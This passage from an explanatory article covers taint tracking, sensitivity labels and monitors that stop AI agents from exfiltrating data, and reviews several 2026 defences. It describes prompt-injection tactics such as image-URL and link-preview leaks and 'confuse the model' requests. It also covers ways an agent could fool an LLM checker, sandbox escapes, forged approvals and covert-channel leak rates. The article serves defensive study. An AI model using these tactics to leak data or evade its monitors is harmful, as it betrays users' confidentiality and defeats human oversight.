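|---|---|---|
| Email | The To, Cc and Bcc fields, and the members of any mailing list | Everyone found |
| Message in a Teams channel | The channel's current members | Every member |
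| Comment on a GitHub issue | Whether the repository is public | Anyone, if it is; otherwise the people with access |
| Link or image in a chat window | The host in the web address | Anyone, unless the company has approved the host |

The last row covers a leak that can happen without a send command. If the agent's answer to Ana includes an image, her chat window may fetch it automatically, which sends the image's full web address to its host. An agent can write Ben's salary into that address.

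A membership lookup returns only the channel's current members. If Dana joins next month and can read the channel's history, she will see messages the system approved before she joined.

The agent also needs the right address. Carol's invoice could give a false new address for Ben, for example. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) presents a policy language that lets a company specify, before a task starts, where an address may come from. In the paper's main example, an agent has to send the public fields of a private report to Alice, at most once. It may use only the address in one field of one directory lookup, so it can't use an address from an email. If a second lookup returns a different address, Agenra rejects both for the rest of the task. It doesn't protect against tampering with the directory.

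### Labels in the Model Context Protocol

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format for messages between an agent and the servers that run its tools. These messages have a field called `_meta` for extra information. Microsoft's prototype puts labels in this field, so software that doesn't support labels can ignore them.

One label covers the whole call, and each argument can have its own. A Teams message about salaries might have these labels:

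```
whole call:    untrusted, public
message text:  trusted, {Ana, Ben}
```

The first line records that the agent chose the call after reading something an outsider could have written. The second line gives the text a stricter sensitivity label, for example because the agent kept the text in a variable. An argument without its own label takes the label of the whole call.

A server can publish a policy for each tool in the same way. Before a call, a policy engine evaluates the policy and decides to allow the call, deny it or ask the user. Microsoft's sample policy for Teams works in this order:

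1. If the agent chose the call in a trusted context, allow it.
2. Otherwise, look up the channel's members. If all of them may read the text, allow the call.
3. If some of them may not, ask the user and list those people.

In the GitHub attack, the server supplies the labels that stop the agent from posting private text on the public issue. An agent that had read only the public repository could have commented without asking anyone for permission.

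The export rule would stop the agent from sending Marco the sales figures on its own. If a company copied the Teams policy for email, the outcome would depend on how the mail server labelled incoming mail. If it labelled all incoming mail untrusted, Alex would have to approve the reply. If it labelled mail from colleagues trusted, the first rule would allow the reply before checking any readers, and Marco would get the sales figures.

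The prototype covers few tools so far. GitHub's MCP server can attach labels to its results, and the coding agent GitHub Copilot CLI has an experimental setting for tracking them. For other servers, Microsoft provides a gateway that adds labels outside the server. Someone has to describe each tool's output, write a function that carries labels from its arguments to its results, and choose a policy. For a compression tool, that function would copy payroll.csv's label to the archive.

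A simpler option uses hints that MCP tools can already include. A read-only tool that stays inside the company's systems can always run. A tool that contacts the outside world, such as a web search, can run only if all its arguments are public. A destructive tool may always require the user's approval. These rules need no custom code, but they depend on developers describing their tools correctly.

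### Declassification and relabelling

Declassification means deliberately lowering the sensitivity label of data so that the data may be released. Changing the label on payroll.csv to Public does not remove the salaries from the file. The lower label is justified only if a tool has removed the secret or someone with authority has decided that the new readers may have it.

In Agenra's example, the private report is Confidential, and only Public data may go out by email. A tool called Sanitize selects the report's approved fields, and the policy labels its output Public. Shivakumar and colleagues point out that this label relies on an assumption about what the tool does, because Agenra doesn't inspect the output. Suppose Ana's company wrote a similar tool that drops the salary column of payroll.csv but keeps a column of comments. If one comment reads "raised to 150,000 in May", the tool's output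 is labelled Public even though it contains Ben's salary.

What Agenra can guarantee is that secret data passes through such a tool before leaving. Every ordinary operation on inputs x₁, …, xₙ must satisfy

L(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ L(xₙ) ⊑ L(output)

where L here stands for the sensitivity level. Only designated release tools may lower the level. If text derived from payroll.csv has become Public, at least one release tool must therefore lie on every path from the file to the text. The proof assumes that the system records every input and that the sources have correct labels. It says nothing about whether the release tool works.

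A Public label also doesn't show that a text is the right one to send. Shivakumar and colleagues found that their first policy would let the agent send Alice unrelated public text instead of the report, so they added a rule that the message must come directly from the Sanitize tool. The agent could still run Sanitize on text an attacker had written, so another rule requires the tool's input to come from the private report.

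#### Compression, encryption and redaction

Compression never justifies a lower label, and encryption does so only while a trusted service keeps the key out of reach.

Redaction can justify a lower label if it removes the secret. A tool that copies approved fields into a new file is easier to trust than one that searches for forbidden text and deletes it, which must recognise every form the secret might take. For the support desk, a tool could produce a report containing only an error code from a fixed list and the name of the column that caused the error. The company could examine that tool once and then release its output without further checks. It couldn't do the same for descriptions in the agent's own words, because they have no fixed format.

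### Robust declassification

Even a well-made release tool can do harm if an attacker decides when the agent uses it. Robust declassification requires that untrusted data cannot trigger a release. If Carol's invoice is in the agent's context, the agent must not release payroll data on its own, however convincing the invoice is.

Kolluri and colleagues enforce this with their either-or rule for email, and the Teams policy follows the same logic:

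| Context | Everyone may read the data | Someone may not |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted | Allow | Allow, as a deliberate release |
| Untrusted | Allow | Stop or ask |

In a trusted context, the rule therefore treats a mistake as a deliberate release, whether the agent attaches the wrong file or Ana asks for the wrong one. Kolluri and colleagues assume that the user and the planning model are trustworthy, and say their method does not guard against a model that misunderstands a task.

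Robust declassification doesn't require a company to accept this. It forbids releases that untrusted data triggers, but the company needn't count every action in a trusted context as a release. For payroll data, it could require both a trusted context and Ana's explicit approval whenever a recipient is outside the reader set. She would have to answer more questions, and she could still approve the wrong file.

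### Blocking the call

When a check fails, the safest response is to refuse the call and leave the label as it is. How many tasks the agent can still complete depends partly on what it learns from the refusal. *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) tested three responses on AgentDyn, a benchmark of shopping, GitHub and everyday tasks with planted instructions. Compared with an agent that had no defence, ending the task at the first violation lowered the completion rate by 36.2 percentage points, and returning a general warning lowered it by 10.5 points. Explaining which rule had failed and which data the agent could use instead raised it by 6.5 points. Attack success was close to zero with all three responses.

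Such feedback would also help an agent that is trying to leak data, so the system could limit it. If an email would send payroll.zip to Carol, the system could report that she isn't a permitted recipient without suggesting another way to send the file.

### Asking a person

Ana can approve a release that a fixed rule would refuse, such as the description for the support desk. But frequent requests tire people, so Kolluri and colleagues measured how many an agent would make by counting approvals across all the AgentDojo tasks it completed and averaging the totals over five repetitions.

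With OpenAI's o3-mini, an agent that asked before every consequential action needed 48.2 approvals. Checking labels first and asking only when the check failed reduced this to 32.4, with the same completion rate. FIDES, which hides untrusted text in variables, needed 18.8. With o4-mini, FIDES needed 36.8 approvals and Prudentia, whose planner knows the policies, needed 19.2. Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks than FIDES, 73.2% compared with 75.7%.

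Prudentia asks the user for fewer approvals partly because it can ask them to endorse an email, which marks it as trusted, instead of approving each action. If an email contains ten tasks for the agent, one endorsement could replace up to ten separate approvals.

Kolluri and colleagues considered a similar option for secrecy, in which the user would lower a file's sensitivity label once, but decided against it. Whether a release is appropriate depends on the situation, and a request about one particular call captures that situation better. If Ana made payroll.csv public so that the support desk could see one row, the agent could later send the whole file to Carol.

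These counts probably understate the burden on Ana. The experiments involved no human reviewers. Kolluri and colleagues counted the calls that broke the policy and assumed a user would approve them. They left out failed tasks, in which the agent often kept repeating a refused action. Their policy also let the agent send data without asking whenever its context was trusted, so a stricter rule for payroll data would produce more approval requests.

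#### What an approval covers

An approval can be narrower than declassification. In Agenra, a reviewer approves a single use of one exact call, including its recipient and contents. If the agent edits the text afterwards, it needs a new approval, even if it produces the same words again. A failed send also uses up the approval, because the message may have gone out before the error.

The approval doesn't change any label and can't override the rule that only Public data may leave. Under such a policy, Ana couldn't approve sending the raw payroll file to the support desk. She would need a release tool that produces a Public version. Microsoft's sample policy, by contrast, lets the user approve a message for people outside the reader set.

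Labels can also make the request more informative. Ana learns little from a dialog that shows only the file name payroll.zip, and even less if the name is archive.zip. Microsoft suggests showing where untrusted data came from, what data the call would share and with whom. Here, the dialog could show that the archive contains data from payroll.csv and that Carol may not read that file.

If a permission runs out when used, widening it can block work that the policy used to allow. Suppose a policy lists one permission to send a report to Ben, followed by one to send a report to Dana, and Agenra uses the first permission that fits. The company then widens the first permission to cover either person. If the agent writes to Dana first, it uses up the wider permission. The remaining one covers only Dana, so the agent can no longer write to Ben. Shivakumar and colleagues built a checker for such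 changes and tried it on 51 revisions they had written. It certified all 21 that kept every intended workflow and none of the 30 that lost one. A change that passes this check can still allow a new leak, even though it keeps every old workflow.

They also tested agents with fixed attacks that asked for the raw report. Without a guard, an agent using a Qwen model sent it in 15 of 20 runs. With Agenra it never did, but a simpler handwritten guard did equally well. The attacks still disrupted the work. The Qwen agent delivered the proper report in only 5 of 20 runs, whether it had Agenra, the handwritten guard or no guard.

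### Asking a checker that sees the source

A language model can make some of these decisions in place of a person. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, argue that the agent's own model is a poor choice for this, because the person asking for the data also controls much of the conversation it reads. They designed three attacks that look like ordinary work and contain no planted commands. In Ana's office, they might look like this:

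- Carol shares a document about a joint salary review and asks the agent to fill in its section.
- Carol lists several possible salaries for Ben and asks the agent to delete the wrong ones. The entry that remains is his salary.
- Carol emails the agent and asks it to reply only "completed", while a shared page asks it to write the details there.

They compared FlowSeal, their own system, with a set of instructions that told the agent to verify identities and obtain consent before sharing anything. They ran 105 scenarios three times each and measured the share of sensitive items that leaked:

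| Attack | Instructions to the agent | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Fill in a shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Delete the wrong entries | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Split the request across two channels | 43.8% | 2.2% |

FlowSeal intercepts every outgoing call, allowing those to trusted recipients and refusing those to blocked ones. For any other recipient, it gives a separate model the proposed text and the protected records that the recipient may not see, and the model answers only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". The model doesn't see the conversation, so Carol's story about a joint review can't affect its answer. Because it has the source records, it can also match "a hundred and fifty thousand" to Ben's salary, which a filter that checks only the outgoing text might miss.

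Shim and colleagues also measured what the checker contributed, using the shared-document attack and a set of harmless requests. When they replaced it with a rule that blocked every unknown recipient, the agent completed none of the harmless requests, because every recipient in that test was unknown and the data's owners ignored requests for permission. When they let everything through, 24.9% of sensitive items leaked. With the checker, the agent completed 72.4% of the harmless requests, close to the 75.9% it completed with the best prompt-based defence.

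FlowSeal did much worse when sharing private data was appropriate. In a test where the owner would consent if asked, it delivered 32.7% of the requested items, while the other defences delivered 61.0% to 85.6%. Shim and colleagues attribute this to the agent asking for consent less often. FlowSeal's low leak rate is therefore partly the result of excessive caution.

In a small trial with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the leak rate in the deletion attack was zero with FlowSeal and 34.7% with another model-based defence. The trial counted only facts that appeared word for word on a page, so it would have missed paraphrases. On the main benchmark, FlowSeal made each run cost about two cents more and made runs 37% slower.

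#### Where the checker can fail

Shim and colleagues prove that protected data can reach an unauthorised recipient only if the checker wrongly returns "SAFE". That is a large exception, since the checker is a language model. They report that it sometimes misses paraphrases, and that an agent might split one fact across several messages that each look harmless.

They assume an honest agent and do not test prompt injection. An agent that Carol controls could include instructions to the checker in the outgoing text. After a refusal, FlowSeal also lets the agent rewrite the message and try again, which gives a dishonest agent more chances to find wording that passes.

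A checker is also of little use for payroll.zip itself, because a language model can't reliably tell what a compressed file contains from its bytes. The system would have to unpack the archive first or rely on its label. A checker is better suited to the description for the support desk. Even there, Ana's company could use the answer "SAFE" to decide whether to show her a message, and let her decide whether to release it.

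### Checking only the destination

A simpler policy allows data to go to a recipient if the user's task involves that recipient, whatever the data contains. Summers and colleagues used such rules for AgentDyn, although their system can also trace which records a value came from. They had a language model write the rules for each task and instructed it to restrict the destination of outgoing data, never its contents. They reasoned that if only the person named in the task can receive anything, an attacker gets nothing, regardless of what the message says.

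If the task names a recipient, the email tool accepts only that recipient's address. If the task involves no email, the rule blocks the tool. Sometimes the agent has to find the recipient in a document, for example by reading an account number from a bill. The number must appear in the bill, and a model checks that nobody planted it there.

With Qwen3 235B, the agent completed 61% of AgentDyn's tasks and no attack succeeded, a better combination than any of nine other defences achieved. AgentDyn counts an attack as successful when the agent completes the planted task, however, so it doesn't measure whether the right person receives the wrong file. The two kinds of rule give different results in Ana's office:

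| Action | Destination rule | Labels and the export rule |
|---|---|---|
| Ana asks for payroll.zip to go to Ben; a planted instruction redirects it to Carol | Refused | Refused |
| Ana asks for the calendar to go to Carol; the agent attaches payroll.zip | Allowed | Refused |
| The agent emails payroll.zip to Ben and copies Carol | Allowed | Refused |
| The agent puts a salary in a web address, and the task names no site | Left to a separate check | Refused |
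| Ana asks for the opening hours to go to Carol after the agent has read payroll.csv | Allowed | Refused |

The third row reflects a limit of the software, whose rules couldn't handle fields that contain lists, so the model was instructed to leave Cc, Bcc and attachments alone. For similar reasons, the rules don't cover a `git push`, which uploads code to a repository, if the call names only a local folder. Summers and colleagues did check contents on another benchmark, where one rule uses a model to check whether a file contains a secret key before the agent uploads it.

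The destination rule gives the better result in the last row. It doesn't label data, so it never over-taints, and the agent can send public information after reading a private file.

A company could use both rules to reduce the number of approval requests Ana gets. If the labels forbid a message and her task never named the recipient, the system can block it without asking her, which would stop most attempts to redirect data to Carol. If she did name the recipient, as with the support desk, the system can show her the exact text and where it came from, and let her approve that one message.

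## What must hold for taint tracking to stop exfiltration

A rule about recipients can protect payroll.zip only if the archive has the right label and the agent can't get around the check. The claim that taint tracking stops exfiltration rests on five premises:

1. Every sensitive source has a label.
2. The tracker follows data through every transformation and store, or overestimates where the data went.
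3. The system checks every exit.
4. The agent can't alter the tracker or its labels.
5. The flows that the tracker misses are too small to matter.

If these premises hold and salary data still reaches Carol without approval, the data must have moved by a route that the tracker misses. Otherwise, the data and everything computed from it would have kept the label assigned at the source, and the system would have compared that label with the recipient at the exit. The agent couldn't have changed the label or disabled the check, so the export rule would have refused to send the data to Carol. The last premise limits how much data can move by untracked routes.

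If any of the first four premises fails, the whole file can leak, even if the others hold. A proof about a policy, such as the ones for Tether, isn't enough to rule out a leak, because it can't show that Ana's company labelled all its files.

### Sensitive data without a label

Suppose Ben saved a copy of payroll.csv as march-backup.csv, and nobody labelled the copy. In Tether, a company assigns the first labels by writing patterns for file paths. A file that matches several patterns gets the join of their labels, and a file that matches none gets a default label. If the default is Public, as in Sistla and colleagues' inventory example, the agent could send the backup to Carol without transforming it.

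The best reply is a strict default, which gives any file that matches no pattern a label as restrictive as the one on payroll.csv. The company then lists the folders whose contents are public. If it forgets a pattern, the system blocks a harmless email instead of releasing the salaries. The drawback is that the agent can't send a new brochure until someone puts it in a public folder.

A file can also have a second name, called a hard link, which a rule about the first name doesn't cover. *Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) describes Zero-Trust Agent Cells, a system that runs a coding agent in a sandbox and passes every request for a file, program or web page through a separate broker. The broker asks for human approval before the agent reads a file with more than one name, and it won't start any program while such a file is in the agent's workspace. This also blocks harmless links, such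 as those git makes when it copies a local repository. A tracker could avoid the problem by attaching the label to the number that the file system uses to identify the file, which is the same under every name.

Ana may also type a secret into the chat, for example by asking whether Ben's tax code is still correct now that he earns 150,000. That figure did not come from a labelled file. If the system labelled everything she types {Ana}, the context label would be {Ana} from the first message, and the agent could write only to her.

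Scanning Ana's messages is less restrictive. The policy language in *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees*, by Balunović, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2024), includes detectors for personal information and secret keys. A system could run them on her messages and add a label when they find something. The detectors will miss some secrets, but a scan that only adds labels can't weaken the existing protection.

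Passwords are better kept out of the chat altogether. An SC Media article from the security company Sophos describes credential isolation, in which the agent calls a tool by name and a separate process supplies the password, so the agent can use the password without seeing it. A compromised agent might still direct this process to the wrong host, so the article recommends tools whose destination the agent can't change. This method doesn't work for salaries if the agent has to read them.

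### Memory, databases and other agents

Many agents keep notes between sessions. In one of Cai and colleagues' test scenarios, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast in its memory on the first day and uses it in an operations report on the fourth. If the memory doesn't store the forecast's label, the tracker has only an unlabeled note written by the agent. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) argues that leaks between sessions are the default in any system that doesn't require labels on memory.

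SPA avoids this by storing a label with each result. Ouyang and Hou (2026) point out in *MemLineage* that planners such as FIDES don't preserve labels when the model writes a summary to memory. Their system signs each memory entry and records which earlier entries it came from. A signature alone would show that the agent wrote the summary, but not what it had read.

Ouyang and Hou estimate how strongly each entry influenced the next, and pass on the mark for untrusted data only if the estimate is above a threshold. In one of their simulations, the estimate starts at 0.9 and falls by 30% each time the agent rewrites the text, so the fifth link has a weight of

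0.9 × 0.7⁴ ≈ 0.22

A threshold of 0.3 would catch the first link and miss the fifth. They address planted instructions and leave the secrecy of memory to other systems. For payroll data, it is safer to give every new entry the full context label, which doesn't weaken no matter how often the agent rewrites the text.

That rule can make a lot of memory unusable, so *AgentKernel* (2026) proposes labeling each entry instead of the whole session. Notes the agent wrote before it read payroll.csv then don't need the payroll label, but notes it wrote afterwards still do, unless the system kept the file out of the model's context.

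A company could also give the agent no memory between sessions. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how someone could use another person's program without it leaking their data to the program's owner. He required such a program to keep nothing from one call to the next. If Ana's payroll agent started each session with an empty memory and scratch folder, it couldn't carry Monday's salaries into Tuesday's task.

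Databases and background processes are harder to empty. Tether can't follow data through them, but it can block access to them. A less drastic option is to label the whole database with the join of the labels on everything written to it. But after one import of payroll.csv, every query result would have the payroll label, even a list of meeting rooms. Labels on individual rows would avoid this, but the database would have to support them.

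Under Lampson's rule, if a confined program calls another program that the user has no reason to trust, the system must confine that program too. The same applies to agents. If Ana's agent asks a second agent to compress the file, either the tracker has to follow the second agent or the export rule has to treat it as an outside recipient. *AgentKernel* never automatically shares highly sensitive memory between agents.

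### Exits that nobody checks

Link previews, like images in a chat window, can leak data through their web addresses. Slack fetches the links in a message to show previews, so this can happen even if the agent writes only to Ana. Balunović and colleagues showed in 2024 that a planted instruction could use such previews to extract a document from two widely used agent systems. The providers fixed the problem after hearing about it.

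Their remedy is a rule that raises an error if the agent reads a Google document or spreadsheet and later sends a Slack message with previews on. The rule checks only the order of the two actions, so it also blocks a summary of a public spreadsheet. A tracker with labels could be more precise by treating a message with previews on as public only if it links to an unapproved host, as Microsoft does for chat windows.

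*An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets*, published by Help Net Security in July 2026, describes a more serious failure involving public comments. It reports tests by Elad Meged of Novee Security on coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI in the vendors' own repositories. In the pattern it describes, a bot reads a bug report, runs shell commands taken from it and posts their output as a comment. One part of the system approves the commands because they look safe, and another publishes the output by default. Neither decision is wrong by itself, but Meged says that together they exposed secrets from Anthropic's pipeline.

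According to Meged, Anthropic fixed each leak he reported, and he then found another. Google's agent failed to enforce a restriction when it ran a command, and later stages of OpenAI's agent trusted files left by earlier stages. All of this comes from Meged, whose job is building agents that test systems for weaknesses. But Anthropic paid him for his findings, and the advisory that included the Google flaw had the highest possible severity score.

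Sensitivity labels would address this combination if the secrets were labeled and the comment counted as a sink. The command's output would get the secrets' label, and the check on the comment would block it even though an earlier check had allowed the command. Meged likewise recommends checking again when a later stage uses the output. He also says systems should stop trusting labels, by which he means verdicts such as "this command is read-only". Such a verdict can become wrong when the command's output goes somewhere new, but a sensitivity label is still correct there because it describes the data.

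*Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* proposes labeling every channel in which an agent can reply, with public chat at the lowest level and a company's own chat at Internal. Logs should be labeled too. A build log that outsiders can read is a public channel. Even a private log of refused calls needs a strict label if it records the text that the system refused to send.

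A company can't be certain that its list of exits is complete, so it should also close every network route it hasn't examined. In Commey's system, only the broker can open a connection, and it checks the destination again if a website redirects the request. The company then has to examine only the permitted services, but it still has to know what each one does with the data, because the broker would treat a message with a link preview as an ordinary message to Slack.

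### Protecting the tracker and its labels

An agent that can edit the table of labels can relabel payroll.zip as public without touching the archive. Commey's results show why this must be prevented. In one experiment, Commey removed the sandbox around the agent but kept the broker and all its rules. Ten attacks in the test suite bypass the broker and act directly on the machine. All ten failed with the sandbox in place and succeeded without it, including one that forged an approval and one that shortened the audit log.

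The tracker, its rules and its labels must therefore be outside the agent's reach. Sistla and colleagues assume that an attacker knows the whole policy but can't alter the monitor. They also trust the operating system's kernel, the tracing layer, the network proxy and the code that translates system calls into actions. These assumptions are common in work on sandboxes, but they aren't always true. SC Media mentions several cases of agents escaping from sandboxes, sometimes because they couldn't finish their task inside.

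Labels that travel with data between systems also need protection against tampering. Ouyang and Hou sign each memory entry together with its trust level, so changing the level without the key invalidates the signature. The program that runs the agent must keep the key from it, because an agent with the key could sign a false label.

A small tracker is easier to check than a large one, but it can still contain mistakes. Commey's prototype has 3,164 lines of trusted code, excluding libraries, and Commey found eight flaws in it while building the tests and reviewing the code. In one, an approval applied to a file's name, which could later refer to a different file. Commey fixed this by tying the approval to the file itself. The tested system includes all eight fixes, but tests can't rule out other flaws.

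### Covert channels and the size of the secret

Even if the first four premises hold, some information can leave by routes that the check ignores, such as covert channels and implicit flows through the agent's choice of actions. Lampson introduced the term "covert channel" for a channel that nobody intended for communication, such as a program's effect on how fast the computer runs. He distinguished covert channels from storage, such as files and messages, and from legitimate channels, such as the bill that a program's owner receives. The bill is supposed to reach the owner, but its amount can reveal something about the customer's data. Similarly, an email to Carol about the opening hours may contain only public text, but the agent may have timed it based on a salary.

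In Lampson's full remedy, the user fixes in advance everything the program puts into such channels, and the system enforces this even if it slows the program down. Ana's agent might have to send Carol exactly one email a day, at nine o'clock, whatever is in payroll.csv. Because enforcement can be burdensome, he also suggested accepting some leakage and limiting its rate.

Whether a limit is enough depends on the size of the secret. Suppose each message reveals one bit through something the label check ignores. A 256-bit key then takes 256 messages. A 10 MB archive takes

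10 × 10⁶ bytes × 8 bits = 80,000,000 messages

| Secret | Bits | One message a second | One message a minute | One message an hour |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ben's salary | 20 | 20 seconds | 20 minutes | 20 hours |
| Encryption key | 256 | 4 minutes | 4.3 hours | 10.7 days |
| 500 salaries | 9,966 | 2.8 hours | 6.9 days | 415 days |
| 10 MB archive | 80,000,000 | 2.5 years | 152 years | 9,100 years |

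A limit of one message a minute therefore protects the archive well but does little to protect the key. It also doesn't protect the salaries inside the archive for long, because an agent that can read them could send only those.

Another reason to keep the key out of the agent's reach is that leaking it can expose the whole archive. Suppose the company encrypts the 10 MB archive, labels the ciphertext Public and sends it to Carol. She then needs only the 256-bit key to read it. At one message a minute, the agent could leak the key in about four hours, compared with 152 years for the archive itself. Changing the key afterwards wouldn't help, because the old key would still open her copy.

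The *Covert Channel Analysis Guideline*, which the US National Computer Security Center published in 1993, makes a similar comparison. A channel of 0.1 bits per second can leak a 64-bit key in less than 11 minutes, which is a problem if the key is valid for eight hours. By contrast, a channel of 10,000 bits per second needs about 200 seconds to leak one satellite image, so in an hour it leaks less than 0.2% of a collection of 10,000 images.

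US government guidance at the time accepted channels below 0.1 bits per second and aimed to reduce faster ones to 1 bit per second where possible. According to the guideline, no specific policy justified these numbers. They came partly from a judgement that 100 bits per second, roughly the speed of an old computer terminal, was clearly too fast. The guideline recommends choosing limits for each use instead, and suggests 0.002 bits per second for the key, so that leaking the key takes at least as long as it is valid.

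Average rates can also mislead when the secret is short. Moskowitz and Kang (1994), in *Covert Channels*, describe a channel in which the first bit takes one unit of time to send and each later bit takes twice as long as the one before. Its long-run rate is zero, yet it can carry four bits in 1 + 2 + 4 + 8 = 15 units. If a unit is one second, Ben's 20-bit salary would take 2²⁰ − 1 seconds to leak, or about 12 days. Moskowitz and Kang therefore propose a separate limit for short secrets, which sets how many bits may leak, in how much time and how accurately.

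They doubted that practical systems could ever eliminate covert channels, because the remedies interfere with ordinary work. In their example, a secret part of a payroll database confirms that it has received a request from a less sensitive part, and the delay before the confirmation can carry information. Removing the confirmation closes the channel, but then the sender can't verify that its request arrived. Their compromise, the pump, stores the request and confirms it after a partly random delay.

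For an agent, the simplest limit is a daily cap on actions that outsiders can observe. The cap has to cover all the company's agents together because parallel channels add up, according to the guideline. It also has to be very low to protect a single salary, since twenty messages a day, at one bit each, could reveal one salary every day. Logging these actions may discourage misuse, but a log often can't show what a channel carried.

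### Keeping sensitive data away from exits

According to Commey, the alternative to information-flow tracking is to ensure that no cell (a confined agent) has both sensitive data and a way to send data outside. For example, a payroll agent that can't send anything outside needs no cap on its messages.

In Commey's tests, the system blocked 58 of 74 scripted attacks and held 14 for a person to review. The other two succeeded by sending a secret to a permitted host in a form that the broker's pattern scan didn't recognise. The broker controlled where the agent could send data but didn't track what that data was derived from. A label on the secret could have stopped both attacks, and so could a cell without a permitted host.

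The prototype can give each cell different tools but not different permitted hosts, so full separation would require separate brokers. Commey didn't test that arrangement. The tests do indicate how much the confinement itself limits the agent, which could complete 43 of 46 single operations but only four of seven longer workflows. The failures included a build that had to start another program.

The rule is stricter than the better-known Agents Rule of Two. As SC Media describes it, an agent should do at most two of three things: process untrusted input, access sensitive systems and change things outside. An agent that reads payroll.csv and sends email satisfies the Rule of Two if it never reads anything untrusted. Avoiding untrusted input protects against Carol's planted instruction, but the agent could still attach the wrong file or leak the salaries for a purpose of its own. Separation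 prevents both because the agent has no way to send the file.

Tracking and separation permit different work:

| Task | Tracking | Separation |
|---|---|---|
| One agent compresses payroll.csv and emails it to Ben | Permitted | Forbidden |
| One agent corrects a salary, then searches the web for a tax rule | Permitted if the query doesn't have the payroll label | Forbidden |
| The payroll agent loads salaries into a database that the tracker can't follow | Forbidden | Permitted if the database has no way out either |
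| The payroll agent runs a program that moves data in ways the tracker can't record | Forbidden | Permitted |

Separation avoids the second premise because it doesn't need a tracker inside the payroll cell, but it still needs the others in some form. If nobody knows that march-backup.csv contains salaries, the company may put it in the cell that has email. The payroll cell must also have no forgotten exit, and the agent must not be able to change its own permissions.

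An agent that uses a cloud-hosted model sends its context to the model's provider, so data can always leave by that route. Commey treats this route as permitted. Under either approach, Ana's company must count the provider as a permitted reader of payroll.csv or run the model on its own computers.

The company needs both approaches when a result has to leave the payroll cell, such as when Ana wants to send payroll.zip to Ben. The agent could put the archive in an outbox folder. A small mail program outside the cell, with no language model, could then label everything in the folder {Ana, Ben} and apply the export rule to each message. The label would be the same whichever compressor, script or database the agent had used. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) similarly recommends starting with access rules that give each agent as little access as possible, then adding flow labels. If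 the mail program could also write to the outside support desk, the payroll cell would again have a route out of the company, and the company would have to limit how much the timing and number of those messages could reveal.
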